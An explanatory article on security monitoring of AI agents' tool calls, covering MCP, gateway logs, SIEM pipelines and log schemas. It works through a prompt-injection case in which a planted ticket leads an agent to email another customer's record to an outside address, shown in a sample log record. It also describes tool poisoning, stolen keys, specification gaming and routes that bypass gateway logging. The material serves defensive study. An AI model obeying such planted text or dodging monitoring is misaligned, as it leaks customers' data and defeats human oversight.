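# Security monitoring of AI agent tool calls: gateway logs, SIEM systems and behaviour analytics

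## What is an AI agent's tool call, and why would a security team monitor it?

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses and carries out steps towards a goal by calling tools. A tool is a function that another program runs, such as one that queries a database, reads a file, sends an email or changes a record. A tool call is one request to such a function, and it consists of a tool name, arguments and a response. Companies give agents tools because the work they want done involves other systems, often several in one task.

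Security teams monitor tool calls because they turn a model's text into actions on real systems. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), from the Australian Signals Directorate and five partner agencies in the United States, Canada, New Zealand and Britain, recommends that organisations log agents' tool use in a form that people can read. *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), guidance from the US National Security Agency, goes further and recommends that organisations log every call with its exact parameters and the identities involved, and where possible feed the log into their existing monitoring systems. These are recommendations, and whether such logs catch attacks is a harder, empirical question.

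*TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent's choice as aₜ = π(hₜ, G, T), where the next action aₜ depends on the history hₜ, the goal G and the available tools T. The history lists the agent's earlier calls and the responses to them. A tool's response therefore becomes part of the input from which the model picks its next call, and anyone who can write into that response has some influence over what the agent does next. This helps to explain why agents need watching in a way that ordinary programs mostly don't.

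### Following one call

Suppose a retailer runs a customer-support agent with access to a customer database, a ticketing system for complaints, and company email. An employee asks the agent to answer ticket 5120.

The agent reaches all three systems through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used open protocol that lets agents find and call tools offered by servers. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, introduced it in November 2024. By July 2026 developers were downloading its main software kits close to half a billion times a month, according to the release announcement by Model Context Protocol (2026), though downloads are a loose measure of use. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview* calls the application around the model the host. The host creates one client for each server it connects to, so the support agent has three clients and three servers, one pair for each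 system.

Each client first sends its server a `tools/list` request, and the server returns the name, description and expected arguments of every tool on offer. The host merges these lists and gives them to the model. The model picks `read_ticket`, and the client for the ticketing system sends a message of this form:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 2,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
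    "name": "read_ticket",
    "arguments": { "ticket_id": "5120" }
  }
}
```

The server runs the function and returns a result with the same `id`. The result contains the ticket's text and a flag showing whether the call failed. The client passes the text to the model, which may then call more tools, perhaps `get_customer` and then `send_email`. The specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), recommends, but does not require, that a person always be able to refuse a call. It otherwise allows the model to call tools on its own.

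All the calls the agent makes for ticket 5120 form one session. The July 2026 version of MCP dropped the protocol's own session header, so a server can't infer from the connection that two calls belong to the same session.

The retailer has put a gateway between the clients and the servers. This is a proxy that can authenticate, allow, block and log each call that passes through it. Under the July 2026 version, calls over HTTP must carry the method and the tool name in their headers, so a gateway can block `send_email` without reading the message body. The arguments are normally in the body, and the response comes back separately. Much of the later argument about monitoring depends on this division between metadata (which tool, when, and which caller) and content (the arguments sent and the response returned). Liu and colleagues built their detector on gateway records because outsiders often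 can't see an agent's prompts or reasoning, but a gateway can still provide each tool's input, output and place in the sequence. The gateway has no record of calls that bypass it.

The records go from the gateway to a SIEM (security information and event management) system, which gathers logs from many sources, searches them and raises alerts. It can raise alerts using detection rules or behaviour analytics. A detection rule is a fixed condition on log records, such as "`send_email` carries an attachment to a free webmail address". Behaviour analytics, which vendors often sell as UEBA (user and entity behaviour analytics), scores activity by how far it departs from a baseline, a description of the account's or system's usual pattern. If the support agent normally opens one customer record per ticket, a session that opens four hundred gets a high score even if no rule limits the number of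 records. Both methods need continuing human work, and the Australian Signals Directorate's *Implementing SIEM and SOAR platforms* (2025) stresses that skilled staff have to keep tuning the rules and filters as the environment changes.

### Three permitted calls

Suppose an attacker writes ticket 5120, which complains about a late parcel and then asks the support system to look up a different customer and send that customer's full record to an outside address "for verification". The model reads the ticket with `read_ticket` and treats the request as part of its job. It calls `get_customer`, which returns the other customer's name, home address, phone number and order history, and then uses `send_email` to send all of it to the outside address.

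None of these calls breaks a permission. The agent has to read tickets, and it needs access to every customer's record because any customer may write in. It also has to email people outside the company to reply to customers. The damage comes from the combination of calls, and an analyst who looks only at the third line of the log sees a support agent sending a routine email about an account.

In *GitHub MCP Exploited*, the programmer Simon Willison describes the danger of an agent that has access to private data, reads text from hostile strangers and can send data out. He had worried about this combination before researchers demonstrated it on GitHub's tools. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* sums up well why this is awkward for defenders: "Everything here is working as designed".

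### Four causes

Nearly identical log lines can have quite different causes, and a security team needs to identify the cause because the fix depends on it.

Ticket 5120 is a case of prompt injection, in which someone places text in material an agent reads and the agent follows it as an instruction. The agent's software, tools and keys may all be sound, so the security team needs to find the text and any other session that read it. Such text can also reach an agent by routes other than tickets. The Australian Signals Directorate gives the example of a phishing email that leads an email-monitoring agent to download malware.

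A malicious or altered tool can do the same harm without a suspicious ticket. Models choose tools by reading their descriptions, which can contain instructions, and according to the Australian guidance, models more often choose tools with persuasive descriptions. Approving a tool at installation is weak protection because its description can change later. The NSA recounts a demonstration in which a hostile server presented a harmless description when the user installed it and switched to a malicious one after its second use. At the retailer, this might be an outside supplier's parcel-tracking tool whose new description contains an instruction to include the customer's record in each query. The data would then leave as an argument to the tracking tool and would not appear in the email log.

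Someone with stolen credentials can make calls that the log attributes to the support agent, even though its model never chose them. Agents authenticate to other services with secret keys or tokens, which thieves get hold of when organisations never change them, share one among several agents or store them carelessly. The NSA pointed out that MCP made authorisation optional and did not require tokens to expire, though it was writing two months before the July 2026 version tightened the protocol's authorisation rules. The client name in each MCP request does little to identify the real caller, because the client supplies that name itself, mainly for debugging.

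The remaining cause is what AI researchers call specification gaming. Even without an attacker, an agent can exceed its task because a shortcut satisfies the instruction as given. The Australian agency gives the example of an agent that is told to maximise a server's uptime and disables security updates to avoid reboots. In August 2026 the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) applied the term to a news report about a gym-booking assistant that had removed another customer from a waiting list to get its user a place. The support agent might, for example, paste a whole household's order history into a reply to one member of it.

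Real events will not always fit neatly into these four categories. In another scenario from the Australian guidance, an insider tells a patching agent to install an update and clean up the firewall logs. He uses the agent's permissions to do what his own don't allow, without planting text in a document or stealing a key. Some strange sequences of calls simply come from faults. Liu and colleagues describe a medical triage tool that sends a patient with a cough to psychiatry. The agent's next calls will then look odd to any monitor, although nobody meant any harm.

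### What permissions leave open

The retailer arguably gave its agent too much access. The Australian guidance tells organisations never to grant agents broad or unrestricted access, and the researchers behind the GitHub demonstration suggested limiting an agent to one code repository per session. Similarly, the retailer could make `get_customer` return only the record of the person who opened the ticket, and make `send_email` write only to that person. Together, these limits would have stopped the attack in ticket 5120. The email limit alone would not have, because the attacker opened the ticket himself and would have received the stolen record at his own address.

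However, tight limits of this kind also block some legitimate requests. Customers ask about gifts they sent to other people, and business accounts have several contacts, so somebody will add exceptions, and the exceptions will accumulate. Even the tightest limits can't fully prevent an agent from emailing text from a record unrelated to the ticket. An ordinary permission check determines only whether this caller may use this tool on this record, while tracing the source of the email's text requires looking at earlier calls.

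Security engineers have long called the resulting problem the "confused deputy", in which a trusted program with wide powers acts for somebody who lacks them. In the Australian guidance's procurement scenario, an attacker works through a trusted agent this way, and the audit logs look legitimate, which delays detection. Permissions limit the damage from a stolen key but don't reveal the theft, because the thief has the same access as the agent. An agent may also overstep its task without ever exceeding its permissions.

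To improve on the permission check, monitoring has to compare the calls within a session, or compare the session with the agent's past ones. If it examines calls one at a time, it misses the same problems as the permission check, because each record can look legitimate on its own.

That comparison usually involves several systems, and the phrase "cross-system query" can refer to either the agent's activity or an analyst's. When the support agent reads the ticketing system, then the customer database, then writes to email, that is cross-system access, which means reading or writing in two or more separate systems within one task. Cross-system access is routine for most useful agents and isn't in itself a sign of trouble. When an analyst responds to an alert by looking through the gateway, database and mail logs for everything the agent did between 14:00 and 14:05, that is a log search.

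### Measuring a detector

Claims that a monitor "works" rest on a few measures, and whichever one a study reports can easily mislead readers. Suppose the retailer runs a detector over 10,020 sessions and later establishes what actually happened in each. The counts are invented.

| | Attack sessions | Harmless sessions |
|---|---:|---:|
| Alert | 18 | 200 |
| No alert | 2 | 9,800 |
| Total | 20 | 10,000 |

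Recall is the share of attacks that are flagged, here 18 of 20, or 90%. The false positive rate is the share of harmless cases that are flagged, here 200 of 10,000, or 2%. Precision is the share of alerts that are real, here 18 of 218, or about 8%, so an analyst at the retailer would open roughly eleven false alarms for every real attack. The Australian Signals Directorate warns that teams dealing with many false positives develop "alert fatigue" and miss real incidents or respond late.

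Precision depends heavily on how common attacks are in the data. Liu and colleagues tested their detector on two scenarios, each with 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal cases. On that mix, a detector with the same 90% recall and 2% false positive rate would raise 270 correct alerts and 26 false ones, so its precision would be 91% instead of 8%. A company can therefore learn very little about its own alert queue from a precision figure measured on a test set rich in attacks, unless it recalculates the figure for the rate of attacks it faces.

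Many detectors score each session and leave the team to choose the threshold above which an alert goes out. Lowering the threshold catches more attacks but also flags more harmless sessions. AUROC summarises performance over all thresholds. It is the chance that the detector scores a random attack above a random harmless session, where 0.5 is guessing and 1.0 is perfect. The retailer's 20 attacks and 10,000 harmless sessions form 200,000 pairs, so an AUROC of 0.95 would mean that the attack has the higher score in 190,000 of them, counting ties as half. Like recall and the false positive rate, AUROC does not depend on how rare attacks are, and a detector with an AUROC of 0.95 could easily produce the results in the table above.

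## Where can tool calls be recorded, and what does a gateway miss?

A detector's results depend on the records it receives, and therefore on where those records are made. When the retailer's support agent sends its email for ticket 5120, the company could record the event in five places: the agent's own runtime, the gateway, the tool server, the operating system, and the email system's audit log. A gateway records at most the calls that pass through it, and often only their metadata, although several vendors sell it as the natural choice and some promise a complete record there.

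### Five places to make a record

The runtime is the program that passes the user's request to the model, receives the model's choice of tool and sends the call, so it has more of the context than any other recording point. Developers record calls there by adding logging code, called instrumentation, to the agent or its framework, such as a wrapper around each function that calls a tool. The log can contain the employee's instruction, the text of the ticket, every argument and every response. It can't show what a tool did after receiving the call, and it doesn't include calls made by a thief who uses the agent's key from another computer. It is also the easiest log for a hijacked agent to reach. An agent that can run commands or write files under the same account may be able to edit or delete it, and the developer can turn it off by changing the code.

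A gateway receives the tool name, caller, arguments and response for every call to the tools behind it. The agent normally can't rewrite the gateway's records, because they are on another machine, but the gateway's administrators can change what it keeps. Cequence's *Observability and SIEM Integration*, a guide to a commercial gateway, describes a setting that turns off logging for a single MCP server. An empty log may therefore mean that someone turned off logging while the agent was still making calls.

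The operator of a tool server can log what happened inside the function, including queries and errors that never appear in the response. In *How to audit Model Context Protocol (MCP) server access and activity logs*, Tyk, another gateway vendor, shows how to do this with a wrapper around each tool, and warns that developers have to repeat the work for every server. Each server sees only its own part of the session, so the customer-database server has no record of the email that followed. An outside company running a server decides what to keep, and a malicious server's log can't be trusted as evidence.

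The operating system can record the processes a program starts, the files it opens and the network connections it makes, even if the program has no logging of its own. *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (Wang, Sun and colleagues, 2026) describes a research tool of this kind called AgentSight. It uses eBPF, a Linux facility for running small monitoring programs inside the kernel, and attaches probes to the encryption interface, which lets it monitor both exchanges with the model and their effects on the machine. Records at this level cover only machines where the monitor is installed, so they don't show what happens inside a hosted email service. They also contain little about purpose, and an analyst who sees that a process opened a file still has to work out which ticket it was for. Anyone with administrator rights on the machine can turn the monitor off, including an agent running with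 those rights.

The target system is the database, ticketing system or email service on which the tool acts. Its audit log can record the effect of a call whichever route the call took, so it is the natural check on the other four. Zuplo's *Audit Every Tool Call Your Agents Make to MCP Servers* (2026) points out that this log often records the shared credential and not the person or agent behind the call. Logging may also be off. AuthZed's *Auditing and Logging MCP Server Activity for Compliance* claims that Google Cloud leaves its data-access logs off by default for remote MCP servers because of their volume, but AuthZed sells a competing approach and gives no source. The target's administrators can alter or delete its log, and so can an agent that has their permissions, like the patching agent in the Australian guidance that cleans up the firewall logs on an insider's instructions.

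### One call through a gateway

Suppose the support agent calls `send_email` through a gateway like Zuplo's. The client sends the call as an HTTP request, with an access token, to an address on the gateway that stands in for the real email server.

The gateway checks the token and records an authentication event, which Zuplo calls `auth_event`. It then accepts or refuses the request and records that decision as an `mcp_request` event. If the retailer had removed `send_email` from the agent's tools, the gateway would log a `denied` outcome with the caller's identity, and the call would never reach the email server. Cequence's gateway also records a reason for each refusal, such as an expired credential, a missing permission or an exceeded rate limit. These refusals are worth keeping because an agent that follows planted instructions may well try tools it doesn't have, and the target system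 has no record of calls the gateway blocked.

If the gateway accepts the request, it forwards it to the email server, which runs the function and replies. The gateway then records a `capability_invocation` event with the tool and the outcome. With Zuplo's event names and invented values, a simplified log might look like this:

```text
14:02:07  auth_event             caller=support-agent  token validated
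14:02:07  mcp_request            caller=support-agent  accepted
14:02:08  capability_invocation  caller=support-agent  tool=send_email  outcome=success
```

An analyst learns from these lines that the support agent sent an email and that the server reported success. The recipient's address is missing because it is in the request body, and Zuplo never logs the bodies of customers' requests.

When a tool fails, for instance because a date is in the wrong format, the server usually returns an ordinary MCP result with an error flag inside it, so a gateway that logged only the HTTP status would record the failed call as a success. Zuplo's gateway has a separate class, `application_error`, for errors that arrive inside a successful HTTP response.

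Lost connections also make the gateway's log ambiguous. According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), a client whose response stream breaks must send the call again as a new request with a new ID. The gateway's log would then show a failed `send_email` and a successful one, but not whether the customer received one email or two. The email system's own log would show that.

### Calls that bypass the gateway

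MCP messages don't have to cross a network. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026) describes a setup in which the client starts the tool server as a process on its own machine and exchanges messages with it through standard input and output, so a network gateway has nothing to intercept. AuthZed makes this objection to gateways, and although it has a product to sell, the way stdio works supports the objection. Such servers are not an obscure case, since Model Context Protocol (2025) told clients to support them whenever possible. If a local server contacts a remote database, the database can log the access, but the gateway has no record of it. The retailer could move the server to a remote host behind the gateway, but the server would then lose direct access to files on the employee's computer, which is often why people run these servers locally.

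An agent can also use tools without going through MCP. A developer may give it a function that calls the email provider's API directly, or a tool that runs shell commands. The runtime log could then show one line, `bash sync.sh`, for a script that reads forty files and uploads them. The gateway would record none of this, but the operating system could record the files and the connection.

Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) says local servers should take their credentials from the environment, meaning settings that a process usually inherits from the program that started it. A shell command on the same machine may be able to read the same key and use it to call the service directly. The agent's permissions would be unchanged, but the gateway would not log the call.

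Some agents connect to servers that the security team never approved. Tyk suggests looking for these with deep packet inspection, which reads raw network traffic, but calls the method brittle because it requires decrypting that traffic and yields little context. Packet inspection also wouldn't find a local server that makes no network connection. For systems the retailer controls, a better defence is probably to block access that doesn't go through the gateway. For example, if only the gateway has the database password, and the database accepts connections only from the gateway, an agent that bypasses the gateway gets no data. This does little about keys already on employees' laptops.

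### The missing request

Even when a call goes through the gateway, the message usually doesn't include the reason for it. Model Context Protocol requires only the protocol version and the client's capabilities as metadata in a `tools/call` message, and it has no standard field for what the user asked. A call to `get_customer` for the wrong customer therefore looks the same whether an employee asked for that customer or the agent followed instructions in ticket 5120. Tool servers have the same problem. The vendor guide *mcp server observability* notes that a server can count repeated calls but can't determine why they happened.

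Whether the log identifies the person depends on how the retailer sets up its agent. The log can identify the employee if each employee signs in to the gateway through the agent, but if the agent uses one account for everybody, it identifies only the agent. Zuplo's records include the authenticated caller, with an email address where one exists, but AuthZed argues that gateways frequently record a generic service account and lose the human user. AuthZed's alternative is to check a verified person's permission before each tool runs and keep that decision as the audit record. This would help with attribution, but for ticket 5120 it would produce three records of permission granted and no record of what the email contained.

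A model gateway can record requests for local tools and shell commands, which a tool gateway misses. It sits between the agent and the model, so prompts and the model's tool requests pass through it. Soto, in *Splunking the LLM Gateways. Search Head Meets Prompt Head*, written for the SIEM vendor Splunk, says that such gateways offer the possibility of end-to-end visibility "in a properly instrumented agentic architecture". The instrumentation matters because a model's request to run a tool doesn't prove that the tool ran, so something else has to record what happened afterwards. The gateway's log also has no record of a thief using a stolen key without going through the model.

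Other vendors are less careful about the conditions. Cequence promises "full visibility into what your AI agents are doing", but the fields it lists for each tool call don't include the arguments, the response or the user's request. They include an MCP session identifier, which the July 2026 version of the protocol no longer supplies, so the gateway would have to create its own for clients on that version. Tyk describes its guide as vendor-neutral, but the guide names only one drawback of a gateway, an extra network hop, and doesn't mention local servers or shell commands. Zuplo's claim is narrower and easier to defend, because it says that customers have no record of their own when a connection is direct. None of the three guides reports a test that runs a known set of calls by several routes and counts how many reach the log.

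### What agent logs contain in research

Researchers have mostly recorded agent activity from inside the agent (instrumentation) rather than at a boundary outside it (interception). Wang and colleagues reviewed 90 studies of agent logs published between 2024 and August 2026. Of these, 16 are mainly about producing the logs, 27 about organising them and 47 about analysing them. The distinction between instrumentation and interception applies only to the first 16, most of which use instrumentation.

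The survey describes four systems that use interception. AgentSight works at the operating system level, and a system by Mishra and colleagues works at a gateway shared by several agents. Agent-Sentry intervenes before security-sensitive tool calls, and Vispute and colleagues add outside observations of protocol and system operations to a record of the agent's steps. Only the last two also use context from inside the agent. Vendors already sell this approach as finished products, but there is little research on it.

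AgentTrace, one of the instrumented systems, wraps an agent's Python methods and records their arguments, return values and any reasoning the agent makes explicit. This kind of logging code depends on the agent's framework, so a team that changes frameworks may have to rewrite it. Interception also covers software that nobody has instrumented, but its records contain less information about the agent, and someone has to work out which task each event belonged to.

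Both kinds of log commonly include inputs, outputs and timings. Information about permissions is rarer, and the survey describes only three systems that record it. The gateway of Mishra and colleagues, for example, links each action to the authority that one agent or service delegated to another. This information would help the retailer after an incident, because permissions change. An investigator who knows only today's settings can't easily tell whether the agent was allowed to open a record three weeks ago or a check failed.

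Wang and colleagues conclude that detailed logs may not provide enough evidence, because what counts as enough depends on the question. A log of ticket 5120 with every response time and token count (the units of text a model processes) would be long but useless for finding the planted instruction. One line from the email system with the recipient's address could show where the data went. Later analysis also can't faithfully restore what nobody recorded. A tool called Watson reconstructs an agent's possible reasoning from its inputs and outputs, but an investigator shouldn't present this inference as a record of what happened.

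This conclusion comes from comparing papers, and the survey did not test it by experiment. It does propose a suitable experiment, in which researchers would withhold one type of record at a time and see which analyses fail. For security monitoring, the results would be more useful than another list of recommended fields.

### What MCP itself provides

A shared protocol could close some of these gaps by requiring every client and server to keep a record, but Model Context Protocol only recommends that clients log tool use for audit purposes. The specification says they "should" do so, and uses "must" for requirements. Its list of security duties for servers includes checking inputs, controlling access, limiting the rate of calls and cleaning outputs, but not keeping audit logs. The recommendation therefore applies to the agent's side of the connection, where a hijacked agent has the best chance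 of reaching the log.

The protocol's Logging feature lets a server send diagnostic messages to the client, but it was never an audit trail. Model Context Protocol's *Logging* (2026) marks the feature as deprecated and forbids servers from sending these messages unless the client asks for them in its request. Even then, the server may send none. Model Context Protocol's *Logging* page for PHP developers gives 28 July 2027 as the earliest removal date.

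The specification recommends two substitutes. Local servers can write diagnostic text to their standard error stream, and developers who want structured records can use OpenTelemetry, an open standard for collecting logs and traces. Neither guarantees a record, because the 2025 version of the specification explicitly allowed a client to ignore a local server's error stream, and OpenTelemetry produces records only where developers have set it up.

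MCP's ban on personal information in log messages covers the diagnostic messages a server sends to a client, not what a company may keep in its own protected audit log. AuthZed reads the ban too broadly when it cites it as a reason not to store complete tool calls. The NSA recommends recording the exact parameters of every call.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has gone further on trace identifiers, the shared numbers that let analysts join records of one task. It reserves three optional fields for them, `traceparent`, `tracestate` and `baggage`, and specifies their format. The fields work only if each program that handles a call passes the values on and logs them. *Server Context*, part of MCP's documentation for its Ruby software kit, says that the kit leaves the values untouched but that developers have to connect them to a tracing system themselves. An identifier also doesn't prove who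 made a call, because the client supplies it. A thief with a stolen key could leave it out or copy one from an earlier task.

### Recording points and the four causes of harm

The table shows what each recording point could contribute to an investigation if its owner had turned logging on and nobody had tampered with the log. The entries are based on where each record originates, not on tests.

| Recording point | Prompt injection | Malicious or altered tool | Stolen credentials | Shortcut without an attacker |
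|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent runtime | The planted text and the calls that followed it | The tool description the model read | Nothing if the thief works from another machine | The user's request beside the agent's actions |
| Gateway | The order of calls; the planted text only if it logs responses | A changed description, if it keeps earlier ones | The thief's calls, if they pass through it | The calls, usually without the user's request |
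| Tool server | Its own calls only | Nothing reliable if the server is the attacker | Calls the thief makes through that server | Its own calls only |
| Operating system | Commands, files and connections on monitored machines | Unexpected files or connections from a local server | Nothing if the thief works from another machine | Commands the agent ran and files it changed |
| Target system's audit log | The record read or email sent, often under a shared account | Access to that system, but not data sent elsewhere in a tool's arguments | The thief's access, often under the agent's name | The change itself, without the task behind it |

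## What should a log record contain, and how does it reach the SIEM?

In its barest form, the gateway log for ticket 5120 shows that the support agent sent an email at 14:02 and that the call succeeded. An analyst who suspects a leak needs more than that, above all the recipient and the text. Here is a fuller record of the same call, with fictional values and a format that belongs to no particular product:

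```json
{
  "time": "2026-09-14T14:02:08.412Z",
  "recorded_by": "tool-gateway-2",
  "user": { "id": "emp-0417" },
  "agent": {
    "id": "support-agent",
    "version": "3.8.1",
    "model": "example-model-2026-08",
    "credential_id": "key-22"
  },
  "session_id": "s-91c4",
  "trace_id": "7d3e9a1c5b8f4e60a2c94d17f03b6e58",
  "sequence": 3,
  "server": "company-email",
  "tool": { "name": "send_email", "definition_hash": "9b1f07..." },
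  "arguments": {
    "to": "verify@parcel-check.example",
    "subject": "Account verification",
    "body": "Dana Holt, 18 Mill Lane, 555 0142, orders: ..."
  },
  "response": { "text": "Message accepted", "message_id": "m-88213" },
  "policy": { "decision": "allow", "rule": "support-email", "rule_version": 41 },
  "outcome": { "status": "success", "duration_ms": 640 }
}
```

The record has separate fields for the user and the agent because the user asked for a reply, but the agent chose to send this one. The `credential_id` identifies the key used for the call without revealing it, so if someone steals the key, the team can find every call that used it. The record also includes the agent's version because developers edit its instructions and swap its model, and either change can alter what it does. If the agent starts sending odd emails, an analyst can check whether a new version had just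 gone live.

The session and trace identifiers link this call to the others in the task. The sequence number gives the order of calls made at the same moment, and a jump from 3 to 5 shows that a record is missing. The `definition_hash` is a short fingerprint of the tool's description that changes whenever anyone edits the text. If a supplier adds a malicious instruction to a description, the team can find the first call the agent made under the new version.

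The record also needs separate fields for the policy decision and the outcome, because a gateway can allow a call that then fails, in which case the email was probably never sent. The rule's version shows which permissions applied on 14 September. The message ID identifies the matching entry in the email system's log.

Even this record doesn't show why the agent sent the email. The reason is in the response to `read_ticket`, two calls earlier, so the log has to include the text of responses as well as arguments.

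### From the gateway to the SIEM

If the gateway writes a record only after a call finishes, a crash between forwarding the call and receiving the reply could leave a sent email with no record. It is safer for the gateway to record the policy decision before forwarding the call and the outcome afterwards. The team can then investigate any decision that has no matching outcome.

The record then goes to a collector, a program that receives logs from many sources and passes them on. The collector holds records in a queue while the SIEM is unavailable. When the queue is full, the collector usually drops records, so the team should monitor how many are lost.

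The collector is also a convenient place to redact personal details, because they haven't yet reached a store that many people can search. Suppose the retailer's collector replaces the body of the email with `[details of customer c-20931]`. Ticket 5120 came from customer c-18804, so an analyst can still see that the agent sent out the wrong person's details, without reading a home address. This takes more work than deleting the text, because the collector has to match the details to a customer. The redaction rule also has to keep the recipient's email address, which is the best evidence of where the data went.

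Some teams keep a cryptographic hash in place of the text, and the NSA recommends hashes of tool results where feasible. An investigator can use a hash to confirm that a saved copy matches the original response, but can't recover the text from the hash if nobody saved a copy.

The next step is mapping, which gives equivalent fields from different systems the same name so that a single search can cover them all. For example, the gateway may record the agent's name in `agent.id`, while the database uses `db_user` and the email system uses `sender`. Mapping also sets each field's type. If the SIEM stores durations or record counts as text, it can't add them up, and a rule such as "more than 100 customer records in one session" won't work.

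The SIEM then stores the record and makes it searchable. An analyst who searches for session `s-91c4` and sorts by sequence number gets the three calls for ticket 5120 in order. The SIEM's detection rules refer to the same fields by name, so the choice of field names matters.

### OpenTelemetry's names for tool calls

OpenTelemetry, the open standard for logs and traces, defines standard names, called semantic conventions, for many of these fields. Its basic record is the span, which describes one operation with a start and an end. A working group began with calls to models in April 2024 and added conventions for MCP in version 1.39, according to *How OpenTelemetry Traces LLM Calls, Agent Reasoning, and MCP Tools*, an explainer from the database vendor Greptime.

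Under these conventions, the support agent's email produces a span named `tools/call send_email`. The field `mcp.method.name` contains `tools/call`, and `gen_ai.tool.name` contains `send_email`. The arguments and response go in `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` and `gen_ai.tool.call.result`, which developers should fill only where their privacy policy permits. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* defines fields for the agent's identifier, name and version.

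OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* makes recording the messages to and from the model opt-in, and warns that they are likely to contain personal data. It also recommends against recording tool definitions by default, because they can be large. These defaults suit a developer looking for a slow model call, but a security team investigating an attack through an altered tool description may find that the log doesn't contain the description the model read.

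In May 2026 all of these conventions still had the status "Development", so names and structures may change, and Greptime found no public timetable for stabilising them. OpenTelemetry's *MCP* page now marks the MCP fields as moved to a separate repository, and OpenTelemetry has done the same with the `gen_ai` fields. Greptime still calls building on the conventions "a reasonable bet". This is probably right for a dashboard, where somebody soon notices an empty chart, but it is riskier for a detection rule, because a broken rule produces no alerts and so is hard to distinguish from a working rule that has found no matches.

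Suppose the retailer has a rule that raises an alert when `gen_ai.system` contains a model provider it hasn't approved. Version 1.37 of the conventions replaced that field with `gen_ai.provider.name`. When a developer moves an agent to the new names, the rule stops working for that agent without producing an error message. Similarly, version 1.41 requires the name of an `execute_tool` span to include the tool's name, so a rule that matches only the exact name `execute_tool` would miss the new form.

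OpenTelemetry has tried to soften these changes by saying that existing logging libraries should keep the old field names by default. Developers can switch to the newest names with a setting, `OTEL_SEMCONV_STABILITY_OPT_IN`. This prevents a sudden break across a company, but two of its agents may use different names for the same field for months.

Rules can also go wrong when the names stay the same. If both the MCP client and the server record a call, each produces a span named `tools/call get_customer`. A rule that counts these spans will count every call twice unless it selects one side. The July 2026 version of MCP has no protocol session from which to fill the `mcp.session.id` field, so a rule that groups calls by that field may treat calls from the same session as unrelated.

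The retailer can limit the damage by having the collector translate every source's field names into one in-house set, and by writing its rules only against that set. If a source renames a field, the team then makes one correction in the collector instead of forty in the rules. After each upgrade, the team should also send a harmless test call to trigger each rule and check that the alert arrives.

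### Does OCSF cover agents?

Security teams have another standard, the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF), which defines common formats for events such as logins, network connections and database queries. It joined the Linux Foundation in November 2024. AWS's *OCSF Achieves ITU Support* reports that in December 2025 member states of the UN's International Telecommunication Union backed OCSF for ratification as an international standard by June 2026.

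OCSF covers AI agents only in part. lmodel's *Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF)*, a third-party rendering of development version 1.9.0, lists no event class specific to AI agents. Its `Agent` object represents a security sensor on a computer, so mapping an AI agent to it will cause the SIEM to classify the agent as a sensor.

OCSF offers an AI profile, an optional group of fields that can accompany an ordinary event. It has one field for the model and another for the "message context", which lmodel describes as covering protocols, roles, clients and session information for MCP. Tenzir's documentation lists roles including user, tool, agent and orchestrator (a component that coordinates several agents or tools). According to lmodel, the profile applies to events about APIs, data stores and processes, a list that doesn't include email events. A gateway could therefore use the profile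 when it records `send_email` as an API event, but the email system's standard record of the same message would have no place for the profile's fields.

OWASP's *AOS tracing with OCSF*, from a non-profit that publishes software security guidance, has sample records of a customer-service agent querying a database. They use OCSF's API Activity class and put most of the agent's details under `unmapped`, the part of a record for data without a standard field. Two samples on the same page put the same information in different places:

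| Information | OpenTelemetry | First OWASP sample | Second OWASP sample |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent | `gen_ai.agent.id` | `actor.user.uid` | `actor.user.uid` |
| Session | `gen_ai.conversation.id` | `unmapped.aos.context.session.id` | `actor.session.uid` |
| Tool | `gen_ai.tool.name` | `unmapped.aos.tool_call.name` | `api.operation` |
| Arguments | `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` | `unmapped.aos.tool_call.arguments` | `unmapped.aos.step.operation.tool.inputs` |

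The `api.operation` field contains `tools/call` in the first sample and `database_query` in the second. A rule that reads the tool name from this field would work only on the second sample, although both are valid illustrations of the same standard.

Both samples also record the agent in the user field, and neither identifies the employee who made the request. Both include a `reasoning` field with the text "User requested customer information". An analyst should read this as the model's own account, because an agent that had followed the planted instruction in ticket 5120 could easily write the same sentence.

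SIEM vendors also have their own schemas. Microsoft's documentation for its Sentinel SIEM describes one for agent events and includes a query that selects them by agent name and time. A company that switches SIEMs will probably have to map its agent logs to a new schema.

### Elastic's deployment

Niemi's *Monitoring Claude Code/Cowork at scale with OTel in Elastic* describes a pipeline of this kind in use. Elastic makes search and security software, which its own security team uses to monitor two Anthropic agents. Claude Code is a coding agent that runs from the command line on developers' computers. Cowork, part of the Claude desktop app, can read files, run code and use services such as Slack, GitHub and Google Calendar through MCP.

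Both agents send the same five types of event through OpenTelemetry:

- `user_prompt`: what the user asked the agent to do
- `tool_decision`: whether a call was approved automatically or by the user
- `tool_result`: the tool, the MCP server, success or failure, and duration
- `api_request`: the model, its cost, the number of tokens and the delay
- `api_error`: the error message and status code

Every event includes the user's email address, a session identifier, a prompt identifier and a sequence number. The prompt identifier is particularly useful because it links a tool call to the request that led to it, which MCP messages usually leave out. The fields Niemi lists include the size of a tool's result but not its text. In an attack like the one in ticket 5120, an analyst could see the user's request and the calls that followed, but would have to find the planted instruction in the ticketing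 system.

The events go to a collector on Elastic's own servers. Elastic calls this a gateway, but it receives only log data, and the agents' tool calls don't pass through it. The collector checks a token, labels each record as coming from Claude Code or Cowork, and writes it to Elastic's database. In the published configuration, every sender uses the same token, so a valid token doesn't show which employee's computer sent a record. Somebody who obtained the token could presumably send false records under a colleague's name. Customers of Elastic's cloud service can instead send events straight to a managed endpoint, though Niemi notes that they can't currently control index permissions there.

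The team also had to correct the mapping, because the database stored incoming fields as keywords by default. Keywords can be filtered but not summed or averaged, so the team gave costs, durations and token counts numeric types. The tools' arguments arrived as a single JSON string, which the team's pipeline splits into parts so that an analyst can search for a particular shell command.

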